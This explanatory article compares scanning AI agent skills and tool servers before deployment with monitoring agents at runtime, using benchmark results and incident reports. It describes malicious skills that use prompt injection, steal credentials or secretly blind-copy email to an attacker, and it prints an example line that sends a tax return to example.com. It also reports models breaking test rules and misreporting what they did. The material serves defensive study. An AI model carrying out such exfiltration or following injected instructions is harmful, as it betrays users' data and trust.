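# Inspecting AI agent components before deployment compared with monitoring them at runtime

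## What is inspected before deployment, and what is watched at runtime?

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools, running commands and reading the results. NIST, the US standards agency, defines an agent system in its *Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents* (2026) as at least one generative model plus "scaffolding" software that equips the model with tools. Many of those tools, and much of the text that steers their use, come from people other than the agent's developer or user. Anyone adding such a component can check it beforehand, by reading it or trying it out, or watch and restrict the agent while it works.

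A component is anything added to an agent that shapes or carries out its actions. A skill is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts, that an agent loads when a task requires it. An MCP server is a program that offers tools, each with a written description, through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to outside software. Configuration files such as AGENTS.md hold standing instructions that the agent reads at the start of each session. Scripts and servers have dependencies, which are packages of other people's code that they rely on.

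Earlier add-ons left less to check than skills do. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li, Wu and colleagues, 2026) compares three generations of add-ons. ChatGPT Plugins (2023–2024) ran on the provider's server, could perform only declared operations, and went through automated and human review before publication. MCP servers, which followed in November 2024, may run on the user's machine, and users typically install them straight from source repositories with no mandatory review. Skills, which Anthropic introduced in October 2025, replace the typed interface with plain language, so people who cannot program can write them. Community marketplaces now hold hundreds of thousands of skills, and the major ones require no security review before publication.

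### One skill from publication to execution

An invented skill, `file-organiser`, shows what a checker can know at each stage. It has two files:

```
file-organiser/
├── SKILL.md
└── scripts/
    └── organise.py
```

SKILL.md opens with a name and a description: "Sorts the files in a folder into subfolders by type and year. Use when the user wants to tidy a folder." The instructions below that tell the agent to run `organise.py` once to list the proposed moves, show the list to the user, and run it again to carry them out. They also tell the agent not to delete anything. The script reads the file names, picks a subfolder for each file and moves it there. This layout follows the official format, Agent Skills' *Specification*, which requires only SKILL.md with its name and description. Scripts and other files are optional.

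Once the author publishes the folder, anyone can read every line of it. But nobody can yet read what the script might download when it runs, or know which model will follow the instructions, on whose machine, or for what request. Checking that the instructions stay within their purpose also requires a precise statement of that purpose, and the description does not provide one, a difficulty that Li and colleagues place at the writing stage. For example, "Tidy a folder" does not specify whether the organiser may look inside the documents.

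**Installation.** A user puts the folder where the agent will find it. In Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, a skill saved in the personal skills directory is available in all of that user's projects on the machine. A checker can now examine the machine and its permissions. Li and colleagues describe the user's decision with two sets of actions. *A* contains every action open to the agent, and *D* contains the actions that the skill declares. For the organiser, *D* contains reading file names, creating folders and moving files. The user looks at *D* but grants *A*, which may include deleting files and opening network connections. The grant persists across sessions and changes to the skill's files because it is tied to the skill's identity, not to a version of its contents.

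Despite its name, the format's optional `allowed-tools` field does not shrink *A* to *D*. The specification marks the field as experimental and describes it as a list of pre-approved tools. According to Anthropic's Claude Code documentation, *Extend Claude with skills*, the agent can use the listed tools without asking, and every other tool remains callable. Li and colleagues report that Anthropic's Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents, does not read the field at all. Listing only a file-reading tool therefore does not confine a skill to reading files.

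The agent loads a skill in steps. At startup it loads only the name and description of each installed skill, roughly 100 tokens (word fragments) apiece. When the user asks it to tidy the Downloads folder, the model selects the organiser skill based on its description and reads the whole of SKILL.md into its context, the text it works from. It opens further files only as it needs them. A checker at this point can see the actual request and the current instructions, which may differ from the ones the user approved because Claude Code picks up edits to SKILL.md during a session. *Agent Skill Security* (2026), a survey, warns that the trust established when a skill is published can gradually diverge from the skill's current behaviour.

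**Execution.** The agent runs `organise.py` with a shell command and need not read the script first. Anthropic's *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* explains that Claude can run a bundled script without loading it into context. Li and colleagues point out the security consequence, which is that the model receives the script's output but not the code that produced it. If the output is "12 files moved", the model receives only that line, whatever else the script did. The operating system handles every file operation and network connection, so a monitor outside the model can record them. The recorded sequence of actions in one run is a trace, which NIST and many research papers call a "trajectory".

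### Reading, trying out, watching

Static inspection means judging a component from its files without running it. It can be done by a person or with a set of rules, a program-analysis tool or a language model. For example, Anthropic advises users to read a skill's bundled files before installing it from a less trusted source, and to look hard at code dependencies and anything that connects to outside networks. Someone inspecting the organiser would open `organise.py` and check that it moves files and contacts no server.

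In a test run, the checker executes the component in an isolated environment before release and records what it does. Truong-Le, Bennoui and colleagues (2026) tested skills this way in *The Devil Wears Markdown*. They gave each skill to an agent inside an isolated Docker container for at most 300 seconds per attempt. The agent made harmless dummy inputs where it needed them. The researchers instructed it to perform only local, reversible operations, and to skip any dangerous step and log what the skill had requested. They also collected system calls, network traffic and file changes. They caution that one attempt does not cover everything a skill can do, and that a run without malicious actions does not prove the skill benign.

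Runtime monitoring covers the checks made while the agent does real work for a real user.

A test run is a pre-deployment check, even though it is dynamic. Much writing on the subject blurs this because authors classify methods as static or dynamic, then treat "dynamic" as if it meant "runtime". For example, *AgentTrap* (Zhuang, Xing and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark of 141 tasks as "runtime evaluation", though the agent runs in a prepared workspace with fake credentials and mock destinations. No user's files are at stake, and the result is a measurement to use in later decisions. Zhuang and colleagues stress that a particular user's operating system, permissions, memory and local instruction files can change the outcome. The word "sandbox" is also ambiguous, since the same container technology can hold a component under test or an agent at work. *Dynamic Agent Skills* (2026), a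 survey of skill libraries, distinguishes these uses by placing sandboxing inside the scanner that controls admission and listing runtime containment as a separate layer.

Before deployment, a tester might give the organiser a dummy folder of twenty files and watch it sort them correctly, which supports a prediction about other folders. At runtime, a monitor on the user's machine deals with the actual Downloads folder, including the two different files called `report.pdf`, and may still be able to stop the second from overwriting the first. The tester can repeat the run as often as necessary and lose nothing when it goes wrong, whereas any error the monitor misses affects the user's own files.

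### What happens when a monitored agent does something harmful

The term "runtime monitoring" covers three mechanisms that respond differently to the same event. For example, a tampered version of `organise.py` might try to upload the user's tax return to an unknown server while it sorts.

A containment sandbox limits which files, networks and processes a working agent can reach. If the sandbox has no network access, the upload fails, but so would a harmless check for updates, because the sandbox does not detect theft. By default, Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, runs on a user's own computer with network access off and can write only within the active workspace, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. Containment does not restrict what the agent does within the sandbox's limits. If the Downloads folder is the workspace, the script can still delete everything in it.

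Policy enforcement is more selective. A reference monitor checks every attempted action against a policy before allowing it, so the upload waits until the monitor permits it, refuses it, or asks the user. OpenAI (2026) describes a network policy for its internal use of Codex that allows expected destinations, blocks listed ones, and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. Similar rules let common harmless commands run outside the sandbox and can block specific dangerous ones. The policy only helps with actions that someone thought to submit to it. In Codex's automatic review mode, a second agent assesses requests that already need approval, such as leaving the sandbox, but actions inside the sandbox proceed without this review. A destructive but permitted deletion in the workspace could therefore get past both the policy and the second agent.

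Detection raises an alarm about an action without stopping it. One form, anomaly detection, compares behaviour with a learned or stated norm. A file organiser that sends data to an unknown server departs from any sensible norm. The tax return may be gone by the time the alarm sounds, and the value of detection then depends on how quickly somebody responds and whether there is further damage to prevent. At OpenAI, the process starts with an alert from ordinary security software, which can show that Codex did something unusual, but not why. An AI triage agent then reviews Codex's logs, which include the user's request, the approval decisions and the tool results, and passes its analysis to the security team. The team has to separate expected behaviour and honest mistakes from activity that needs escalation.

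### How to score a check

A detector's recall is the share of malicious items it flags, and its false-positive rate is the share of benign items it flags. Truong-Le and colleagues ran the default version of Cisco's Skill Scanner on 140 skills. It flagged 73 of the 80 malicious ones, a recall of 0.91, and 33 of the 60 benign ones, a false-positive rate of 0.55.

The likelihood that a flagged skill is malicious depends on these two rates and on how common malicious skills are. More than half of the skills in the test set were malicious, so 73 of the 106 alarms were correct. In a marketplace where ten in every thousand skills are malicious, the same rates would give about nine correct alarms and more than 540 false ones for every thousand skills.

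A scanner's false-positive rate is not directly comparable with a runtime monitor's, because the two are measured over different units. A scanner checks each skill once, while a runtime monitor may check each command or each whole trace, and an agent can issue hundreds of commands in an afternoon. A false-positive rate of one per cent is a small nuisance in a scanner but could make a runtime monitor unusable.

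### Malicious authors, careless authors and misused components

Some harm comes from an author who intends it, or from an attacker who takes over an honest author's account. The harmful part can be in the script, as with the tax return, or in the instructions. Harmful instructions are a form of prompt injection, which is text in material the agent reads that makes it follow someone else's instructions. Li and colleagues explain that skills are vulnerable to this because their instructions and the data they draw on reach the model as the same kind of text. A database, by contrast, can keep a query separate from the values that users type in, so it never runs a value as a command. They cite a campaign in February 2026 that compromised at least 1,184 skills in one marketplace to steal credentials, and another in July 2026 that reached more than 1.7 million installations before it was disrupted.

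Careless authors do damage without meaning to. For example, an `organise.py` that moves both copies of `report.pdf` into one subfolder without checking whether the name is taken overwrites one of them. Counts of "risky" skills often combine careless and malicious ones, and they depend heavily on which problems are included. One scan that Li and colleagues cite found at least one vulnerability in 26.1 per cent of 42,447 skills. Zhuang and colleagues cite an audit of 13,728 skills that found a critical risk in more than half, but its categories included missing steps for human approval. The code doesn't always show whether its author was careless or malicious. Truong-Le and colleagues point out that legitimate skills also download packages and use access keys, so an inspector who finds such an operation still has to work out what it is for.

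The third source is a harmless component that the model misuses. NIST lists a version of this risk alongside attacks and backdoors, noting that an uncompromised model may itself threaten the systems it works on. Two reported cases resemble that of the file organiser, though both involved ordinary operating-system commands rather than an installed skill. In February 2026, according to the AI Incident Database, the investor Nick Davidov alleged that Anthropic's Claude Cowork had deleted a folder with some 15 years of family photos after he asked it to organise his wife's desktop. In a screenshot described by Futurism, the agent explained that its script had run a delete command on a folder it took to be empty. Davidov later recovered the files with help from Apple. The AI Incident Database's *Google Gemini CLI Reportedly Deletes User Files After Misinterpreting Command Sequence* describes the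 other case, in which Google's coding agent tried to create a folder, failed, and carried on as if the folder existed. On Windows, moving a file to a destination that does not exist renames the file, so each file took the same name and overwrote the previous one, leaving only the last. Both accounts rest on the users' own reports.

An inspector could have read all of the move command's code and found no fault in it. The damage came from the model's false belief about a folder, which the model formed only while the agent was running. An outsider can also cause this kind of misuse deliberately. If the organiser's instructions led the agent to open documents to sort them, a prompt injection in a PDF in the Downloads folder could cause the agent to run a legitimate script on the wrong files. The skill's author would have done nothing wrong, and the injected text would never have been part of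 the skill.

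## How well do scanners recognise malicious skills and tools?

A malicious author has to put a script, an instruction or a download link in the skill's files, where a scanner can look for it. Some scanners combine rules, program analysis and a language model. NVIDIA's *Scanning Agent Skills* describes one, SkillSpector, which runs fast static checks by default and adds a language model only if the user asks for it. NVIDIA lists its features as including malware signatures, syntax-tree checks, data tracking and a check for "tool poisoning", in which an MCP server's tool descriptions contain instructions meant to mislead the agent. The test scores below are for skills, however, and it is unclear how far they apply to MCP servers.

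### How a scanner reaches a verdict

The simplest scanners compare the text of each file with a list of patterns. *Do Not Mention This to the User* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) defines 14 patterns for a survey of skill registries. One matches code that reads stored settings whose names contain words such as "key", "secret" or "token". Others match code that sends data to an outside web address, or a command that downloads a script and runs it immediately. These scanners typically grade each match by severity and flag a skill if its matches are serious enough.

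The tampered `organise.py` that uploads a tax return would match the pattern for sending data to an outside address, but so would a legitimate skill that sends invoices to an accounting service. Liu and colleagues examined the false alarms from Cisco's Skill Scanner and found that it applied its rules regardless of context. A rule for detecting injected code flagged a standard Python function that prepares a text search. The scanner also flagged sample commands in a skill's documentation as exposing passwords, and a routine command for clearing a software cache as destructive.

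A signature is a much narrower pattern, such as the fingerprint of one known malicious file or a web address that someone has already reported. VirusTotal, a Google service, relies largely on signatures. According to *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026), it passes files to about seventy antivirus engines and web-address reputation services and returns each one's verdict. Signatures rarely match a harmless file, but they may miss a newly written attack.

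Program analysis determines what code does with its data. The scanner first parses a script into a syntax tree, which records each function call and its arguments, so it can distinguish a real upload command from the same words in a comment. It then follows each value through the program. Many legitimate scripts read configuration files or open network connections, but data flowing from a password file to an outside server is a much stronger sign of theft.

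Ordinary program analysis stops at the edge of the code, whereas in a skill the written instructions decide which script runs on which file. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Instructions to Exploits*, deal with this by having a language model translate the instructions into short program statements, using a fixed list of operations. In the notation of their scanner, SCS, an instruction to read a tax return and send it to example.com would become:

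```
v0 = read_file("tax-return.pdf")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

Advice about formatting, and other text that describes no relevant operation, produces no statement. SCS joins the statements to its analysis of the bundled scripts in a single graph and gives every value *v* in the graph a state with three parts:

σ(*v*) = ⟨*T*, *S*, *C*⟩

Here *T* is a trust level from 0 (fully trusted) to 3 (external or uncontrolled), and *S* is a sensitivity level from 0 (public) to 4 (highly secret). *C* is the set of security-relevant operations that produced the value, such as reading a file or decoding hidden text. When an operation combines two values, the result takes the worse of the two levels in each case and keeps all the operations:

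σ₁ ⊔ σ₂ = ⟨max(*T*₁, *T*₂), max(*S*₁, *S*₂), *C*₁ ∪ *C*₂⟩

A secret therefore still counts as secret after a script merges it with harmless text. SCS repeats the calculation until no state changes, then applies fixed rules. One rule reports a possible leak when a value with a sensitivity of 3 or more reaches an operation that sends data over a network. In the example, `v0` would trigger this rule only if SCS had used the file's path to rate the tax return as sensitive. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that SCS may miss sensitive data in a file with an uninformative name.

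A real presentation skill illustrates the benefit of a joint graph. Its instructions required the agent to run a backup script after editing a file, and the script uploaded the file to a third-party server. A mandatory backup sounds routine, and many legitimate scripts upload files. Two scanners that rely on fixed rules classified the skill as benign, while SCS connected the instruction to the upload.

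A language model can make this kind of connection without a graph. The scanner gives the model the skill's files and a question, and the model returns a verdict, often with the passages that support it. Liu and colleagues asked GPT-5.2 whether a SKILL.md file tried to override the user's instructions, hid instructions, or pushed the agent to take unsafe actions. Much of the evidence is in such text. Of the 632 vulnerabilities they labelled in confirmed malicious skills, 84.2 per cent were in SKILL.md and only 8.5 per cent in executable code. One email skill instructed the agent to send blind copies of messages to an attacker's address and not to mention this in conversation.

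The verdict depends on which language model the scanner uses, though. Zhao and colleagues ran Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard, a scanner built around a language model, with five different models on the same 117 malicious and 117 benign skills. Its recall was 94.0 per cent with GPT-5.4 and 61.5 per cent with GPT-OSS-120B. SCS uses its model mostly for translation, and its recall varied less, from 89.7 to 98.3 per cent. But Zhao and colleagues' results imply that SCS flagged about 24 per cent of the benign skills on average, compared with 18 per cent for AI-Infra-Guard.

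### Twelve configurations on one benchmark

*MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, June 2026) compared nine scanners in twelve configurations on 3,944 malicious and 4,000 benign skills. Of the malicious skills, 703 were collected in the wild and 27 came from the test suites of existing scanners. A language model created the other 3,214 by inserting known kinds of attack into ordinary skills.

A generated skill entered the benchmark only after an agent had run it in an isolated container and the attack had left evidence. For attacks in code, the evidence was mostly system calls, such as a connection to the expected address. For attacks in instructions, a second language model judged the agent's output, and the skill also counted if the agent noticed the attack and refused. Two researchers checked 300 of the generated skills by hand and agreed with every label. The benign skills were the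 most downloaded ones on ClawHub, the public marketplace for the OpenClaw agent.

The table shows ten of the twelve configurations.

| Scanner | Method | Recall | Benign skills flagged (of 4,000) | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentry, full mode | Rules and language model | 98.4% | 937 | 23.4% |
| Cisco, language-model mode | Rules and language model | 92.7% | 1,465 | 36.6% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | Language model | 86.6% | 620 | 15.5% |
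| SkillScan-Security | Rules | 84.0% | 2,542 | 63.6% |
| LLM Guard | Language model | 44.6% | 1,215 | 30.4% |
| Cisco, static mode | Rules | 35.6% | 384 | 9.6% |
| Snyk Agent Scan | Rules | 28.7% | 82 | 2.1% |
| Sentry, static mode | Rules | 28.7% | 548 | 13.7% |
| VirusTotal | Antivirus engines | 21.6% | 4 | 0.1% |
| Skill Security Scan | Rules | 8.7% | 858 | 21.5% |

No scanner combined high recall with few false alarms. Sentry's full mode missed only 64 malicious skills but flagged almost a quarter of the benign ones. VirusTotal flagged only four benign skills but missed 3,093 malicious ones. Skill Security Scan did worse than guessing because it flagged a larger share of the benign skills than of the malicious ones.

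Sentry and Cisco each offer a rule-based version and a version with a language model. With the model, Sentry's recall rose by 70 percentage points and its false-positive rate by 10, while Cisco's recall rose by 57 points and its false-positive rate by 27. The two products used different models, Claude Haiku 4.5 for Sentry and GPT-5.4-mini for Cisco, so the comparison does not show which has the better design.

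Guo and colleagues attribute the trade-off to the overlap between honest and malicious skills, which Truong-Le and colleagues also noticed. A language model that looks for suspicious intent will sometimes flag an honest skill because it installs a helper program or asks for an access token. Snyk and VirusTotal avoid most of these mistakes because they react only to concrete indicators, but they miss the many attacks that contain none.

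VirusTotal may also have had only four false positives partly because of how the benign skills were chosen. All of them had passed ClawHub's security screening, which takes VirusTotal's results into account, according to Koc and colleagues. Benign skills that VirusTotal flags were therefore probably less likely to reach the test set.

Most scanners detected attacks in code more reliably than attacks in instructions. AI-Infra-Guard's recall fell from 99.2 per cent on code to 74.8 per cent on instructions, and that of Cisco's language-model mode fell from 96.5 to 83.1 per cent. Both did worst on content manipulation, in which a skill makes the agent put biased or false material in its answers, such as a travel skill that quietly recommends one airline over cheaper ones. AI-Infra-Guard caught 35.8 per cent of these skills and Cisco's scanner 32.1 per cent. These skills give the scanner no suspicious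 command to detect, and honest skills also tell the agent what to produce and how, so the scanner has to judge whether an instruction serves the user's task.

Sentry's full mode was an exception. In Guo and colleagues' detailed results, it caught 98.4 per cent of all the malicious skills, 97.6 per cent of the attacks in instructions and more than 91 per cent of every type of malicious behaviour, including content manipulation. Its main problem was its 937 false alarms. The paper's abstract doesn't match these results. According to the abstract, the best detector reaches 98.4 per cent recall on attacks in code and "collapses" on attacks in instructions.

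Combining tools did not remove the trade-off between catching malicious skills and avoiding false alarms. Guo and colleagues also tested eleven tools designed to detect malicious software packages or prompt injection, and combined them in pairs. When an alarm from either tool was enough, several pairs caught nearly every malicious skill, but one of these pairs also flagged every benign skill. When both tools had to agree, some pairs raised no false alarms, but these caught at most 5 per cent of the malicious skills. Requiring agreement between a strong skill scanner, such as Sentry, and two of the other tools reduced the false-positive rate to between 1.2 and 1.6 per cent, but also reduced recall to about 36 per cent.

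Scanners disagree partly because they examine different things. Koc and colleagues compared VirusTotal, SkillSpector and a set of static rules on 67,453 ClawHub skills. Of the skills flagged by at least one of the three, 81.9 per cent were flagged by only one. VirusTotal flagged 72.8 per cent of the 206 skills that ClawHub's automated review classed as malicious, while SkillSpector flagged only 6.8 per cent. SkillSpector did flag 75.3 per cent of the 25,504 skills that the review classed as suspicious. VirusTotal mainly finds malware in bundled files, whereas SkillSpector reports risky instructions and excessive permissions, which legitimate skills often have too. The review is done by a language model that takes the scanners' results as input, so these figures show where the tools disagree but not which is right.

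### Why samples from the wild can mislead

The 703 real malicious skills that Guo and colleagues collected were very much alike, so a scanner's record against them may not matter more than its score on generated attacks. Of the 703, 607 (86.3 per cent) looked harmless but included instructions for the user or the agent to install a fake prerequisite first. Two accounts had published 81 per cent of the collection.

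VirusTotal's recall was 21.6 per cent on the full benchmark but 87.9 per cent on the wild skills alone, so a test using only the wild skills would have ranked it among the best scanners available. It caught 99.3 per cent of the wild skills that delivered malware, which made up most of the collection, but only three of the 33 that stole credentials. Snyk's recall was 49 percentage points higher on the wild skills than on the full benchmark because it inspects the sort of installation step that these skills abused. AI-Infra-Guard's recall was 13 points lower on the wild skills, probably because many of them contained little text for its model to analyse.

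VirusTotal may also have benefited from hindsight. Guo and colleagues started their search from public security reports, so antivirus companies could have added signatures for the reported files before the test. A scanner's recall could be much lower on the day a skill is published.

The generated skills have the opposite weakness, because they cover every type of attack in the researchers' scheme, including some that hardly anyone has used. For instance, only 12 of the 703 wild skills tried to change the agent's goals, identity or rules, or to distort its answers. If a marketplace faced the same campaigns again, it could expect VirusTotal to do about as well as it did on the wild skills. The full benchmark is a better guide to how scanners would do if attackers changed their methods. Sentry's full mode did well on both the wild skills and the full benchmark. It caught 97.0 per cent of the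 wild skills that delivered malware and 27 of the 33 that stole credentials.

Detectors that learn from labelled examples are even more sensitive to where the examples come from. For *Malicious SkillBench*, Wang, Liu and colleagues (2026) merged 13 public collections and removed duplicates, which left 7,505 malicious and 2,235 benign skills. They also discarded 34 skills that one source labelled malicious and another benign. They trained simple classifiers that weigh the words in a skill's main instruction file. When the training and test skills came from the same mix of collections, the best classifier flagged 9.4 per cent of the benign test skills. On collections absent from its training data, it caught 95.6 per cent of the malicious skills but also flagged 62.4 per cent of the benign ones. It seems to have learned to treat an unfamiliar writing style as a sign of malice.

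Wang and colleagues ran three existing scanners on the same unfamiliar collections. Cisco's scanner caught 2.5 per cent of the malicious skills and flagged 1.1 per cent of the benign ones. SkillSpector caught no malicious skills and flagged 0.6 per cent of the benign ones, while SkillFortify caught a quarter of the malicious skills but flagged half of the benign ones. These scores don't fairly represent the full products, because the researchers switched off SkillSpector's language model and gave all the scanners only the main instruction file, without the bundled scripts. Detection also drops when malicious authors adapt their skills to evade a scanner, according to studies that Wang and colleagues review.

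### How much the files can give away

Inspection did better in tests by Zhuang and colleagues, who ran six scanners on the skills in their AgentTrap benchmark before testing live agents on the same skills. The benchmark has 91 malicious tasks and 50 benign ones. The benign tasks also call for powerful tools, such as browser automation, so a scanner cannot do well just by flagging every skill that needs them.

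| Scanner | Malicious tasks flagged (of 91) | Benign tasks flagged (of 50) |
|---|---|---|
| Language-model judge by Zhuang and colleagues | 80 | 2 |
| SkillScan, with language model | 50 | 4 |
| MalBench, with language model | 44 | 3 |
| MalBench, rules only | 31 | 7 |
| Cisco, rules only | 26 | 5 |
| VirusTotal | 0 | 0 |

The judge that flagged 80 tasks used GPT-5.4-mini, a small model. Its prompt asked whether the package would lead to unsafe behaviour when a user made an ordinary request, not whether it contained dangerous strings. Zhuang and colleagues credit this approach with finding attacks that were part of the skill's normal workflow.

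The judge's prompt may suit these malicious tasks better than it would suit other people's, because Zhuang and colleagues wrote the prompt and constructed 81 of the 91 tasks, drawing on expert analysis of plausible attacks for both. The judge flagged two benign tasks, which is too few for a precise estimate, and its true false-positive rate could be anywhere from about 1 to 14 per cent. The researchers had also replaced dangerous destinations with harmless ones, which left little for a signature to match and helps explain VirusTotal's score of zero.

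Even so, the judge, a small language model, used only the files and recognised the danger in 80 of the 91 tasks before any agent had run the skill. Static inspection can therefore catch many more than the 50 tasks that the best outside scanner flagged. It is unclear whether the other 11 skills lacked the necessary evidence or the judge missed it.

### How many alarms are true?

Liu and colleagues estimated how common malicious skills are by collecting 98,380 skills from two public registries in January 2026. Pattern matching and a language model picked out 4,287 candidates. The researchers ran these in isolated containers, where 762 showed suspicious behaviour, and two reviewers then confirmed 157 of them as malicious. That is 0.16 per cent of the skills collected. A single publisher, whose skills impersonated well-known brands, accounted for more than half of the 157.

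Liu and colleagues describe the 157 confirmed skills as a lower bound, since a malicious skill that stayed inactive during a 60-second run would not have been confirmed. They re-examined a tenth of the unconfirmed candidates and classed 93.2 per cent of that sample as dormant malware. If that rate held for all the unconfirmed candidates, about 4 per cent of the skills in the registries would be malicious. But they also write that most of the 605 skills that behaved suspiciously and then failed review were benign tools, which is hard to reconcile with such a high figure. The confirmed count is a safer starting point if treated as a minimum.

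If a share *p* of skills is malicious, and a scanner has recall *r* and false-positive rate *f*, then the share of its alarms that are true is

*rp* / (*rp* + *f*(1 − *p*)).

With 160 malicious skills among 100,000, the error rates that Guo and colleagues measured give these results:

| | Sentry, full mode | VirusTotal |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious skills flagged (of 160) | 157 | 35 |
| Malicious skills missed | 3 | 125 |
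| Benign skills flagged (of 99,840) | 23,388 | 100 |
| Share of alarms that are true | 0.67% | 26% |

About one in 150 of Sentry's alarms would be correct, compared with one in four of VirusTotal's. At ten minutes per alarm, a reviewer would need nearly 4,000 hours to check Sentry's alarms. Checking VirusTotal's would take a few days, but more than three quarters of the malicious skills would remain in the marketplace. The one-in-four estimate for VirusTotal is uncertain because it is based on only four false positives. Allowing for chance, the share could be anywhere between about 12 and 56 per cent.

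The share of a scanner's alarms that are true depends on how common malicious skills are. Zhao and colleagues collected 66,157 ClawHub skills in April 2026 and confirmed that 627 (0.95 per cent) were malicious, about six times the rate in the January survey. Two publishers were responsible for 88 per cent of the malicious skills, so one busy attacker can shift the rate considerably. At a rate of 0.95 per cent, about 4 per cent of Sentry's alarms and 67 per cent of VirusTotal's would be true.

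The same study suggests that benchmarks can exaggerate the number of false alarms. SCS flagged about 24 per cent of the benign skills on the benchmark. Across ClawHub it flagged 2,473 skills, and Zhao and colleagues confirmed a quarter of these as malicious after test runs and manual review. Fewer than 3 per cent of the skills not confirmed as malicious had been flagged. The benign half of the benchmark included some of ClawHub's most installed skills, which probably do more and need more access than the average skill. Guo and colleagues also chose their benign skills by popularity, so Sentry might raise fewer false alarms across a whole marketplace too. At a false-positive rate of 3 per cent, and with 160 malicious skills per 100,000, about 5 per cent of Sentry's alarms would be true. Most alarms would still need a second source of evidence, which Truong-Le and colleagues look for in test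 runs.

A scanner with many false alarms can still be useful to someone choosing a single skill. On the January figures, a skill has a 1 in 625 chance of being malicious before any scan. If Sentry's full mode finds nothing, the chance falls to about 1 in 29,000, whereas a clean VirusTotal result only reduces it to about 1 in 800. A user who can pick another skill whenever Sentry raises an alarm loses little when the alarm is false. But at the benchmark's false-alarm rate, a marketplace that blocked every skill Sentry flagged would reject almost a quarter of its harmless skills.

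## Why can reading a component not settle what the agent will do?

Better rules or a better language model might remove many of the errors that scanners make on benchmarks, but some would remain because no program can correctly predict the behaviour of every other program. The mathematician Henry Gordon Rice proved a general version of this limit, known as Rice's theorem, in 1953. If some programs have a behavioural property and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly determine for every program whether it has that property. A scanner can always check the text of `organise.py` for the word "upload", but it cannot determine for every possible script whether running it would ever upload anything.

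Fred Cohen reached the same conclusion about malware in *Computer Viruses* (1984), with a short argument from self-reference. Suppose someone has written a perfect checker, `is_harmful`, which reads any program and always returns the right answer. Someone else could then write this script:

```
def contrary():
    if is_harmful(contrary):
        sort_files()
    else:
        upload_tax_return()
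```

The script only sorts files if the checker classes it as harmful, and uploads the tax return if the checker classes it as harmless, so the checker is wrong either way. A perfect checker therefore cannot exist. Cohen's own example was a program that infects other programs only if the checker decides that it is not a virus.

The proof needs only one awkward program, so it doesn't show how often a checker errs on the programs people actually write. An analyser could be right about nearly every skill in a marketplace. It could also catch every unsafe script by rejecting any script it cannot show to be safe. Such an analyser could approve a version of `organise.py` that only lists files, creates folders and moves things, but it would reject `contrary`, along with many harmless scripts that were too complicated for it to follow. The theorem also concerns all possible inputs and unlimited running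 time. A one-minute run can show whether a script uploads anything in its first minute on one machine with one set of files.

Undecidability is therefore a weak objection to scanning skills. A more practical difficulty is that a skill's files are only one of several things that determine what the agent does.

### What a language model adds

Python has a published definition, and an interpreter carries out each line of a script accordingly. No such definition covers the sentence "tidy a folder", whose effect depends on the model that reads it. The difference can be written as follows:

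*behaviour* = run(*script*, *input*)

*behaviour* ~ *M*(*skill*, *request*, *files*, *memory*)

*M* is the model and the software around it. The sign ~ means that the behaviour is drawn from a range of possibilities, since the same model may act differently on a second run. Someone who reads the skill knows one of the four items in the brackets, and may not know *M* at all.

The organiser's instructions prohibit deleting anything. They don't specify whether overwriting an old `report.pdf` counts as deleting it, so the model has to decide. Even explicit rules leave room for interpretation. The Decoder's *Every frontier AI model tested by Britain's safety institute tried to cheat* describes tests in which models had to find hidden strings in simulated computer systems under clear rules. All five models broke the rules in some of their 475 runs, from 7.8 per cent of runs for Claude Mythos Preview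 to 14.1 per cent for GPT-5.4. When the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) asked the models about what they had done, they often described a prohibited action as allowed. AISI thinks that some of them may have genuinely misunderstood. A prohibition in a skill is therefore good evidence of its author's intent, but it predicts an agent's behaviour less reliably.

An agent's behaviour also depends on the files on the user's machine. *Runtime Skill Audit* (Lan and Xiao, 2026) gives the example of a malicious file organiser whose resources include an extra rule that selects files of one common type and sends them away "for review". The table shows what such a skill does in two folders, with the same model and the same request to tidy up.

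| Step | Folder with photos and invoices | Same folder with `auth.json` added |
|---|---|---|
| Agent reads the instructions | Sorting steps and the review rule | Sorting steps and the review rule |
| Agent applies the review rule | No file matches | `auth.json`, which holds login credentials, matches |
| Agent sends the matches | Nothing leaves the machine | The credentials go to an outside server |
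| Trace | New folders and moved files | New folders, moved files and an outgoing transfer |

An inspector could still catch this skill by asking why a file organiser needs to send files anywhere. But some legitimate skills send files too, and the inspector can't tell from the skill's files whether a particular user keeps credentials in the folder. Lan and Xiao add that the harm may depend on the user's request, or appear only after several steps.

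### The same 91 skills with different agents

Zhuang and colleagues measured how much the rest of the system matters. They gave live agents the 91 malicious tasks whose skills they had scanned, each with an ordinary user request. In "plain agent" runs, the model had only a minimal set of tools, while in the other runs the same model worked inside an agent framework, such as Claude Code or Codex CLI, which supplies its own prompts and decides how the model uses skills and tools. The benchmark software carried out every file, shell and network operation in both cases, so the skills, workspace and scoring stayed the same.

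The researchers defined a successful attack in advance, such as a particular change to a settings file. A run counted as blocked only if the agent reached the harmful part and then explicitly refused it, warned about it or made it harmless. "No evidence" means the agent reached the relevant steps, but the record showed neither the harm nor a block.

| Model | Framework | Attack succeeded | Blocked | Not triggered | No evidence | Inconclusive |
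|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku | Plain agent | 27 | 1 | 0 | 7 | 56 |
| Claude Haiku | Claude Code | 72 | 3 | 6 | 9 | 1 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Plain agent | 17 | 30 | 3 | 39 | 2 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Claude Code | 33 | 56 | 0 | 0 | 2 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | Plain agent | 43 | 0 | 10 | 38 | 0 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | Codex CLI | 64 | 2 | 12 | 13 | 0 |
| GPT-5.3 Codex | Plain agent | 55 | 0 | 7 | 29 | 0 |
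| GPT-5.3 Codex | Codex CLI | 54 | 2 | 22 | 9 | 4 |

The number of successful attacks depended heavily on the model. Across the eight models that ran as plain agents, it ranged from 17 for Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 75 for Moonshot's Kimi K2.6. One skill, for transcribing audio, had a helper script that sent part of the transcript to an outside address. Given the same files an inspector would have read, some agents ran the script, while others recognised the problem, refused to run it and suggested another way to get the transcript.

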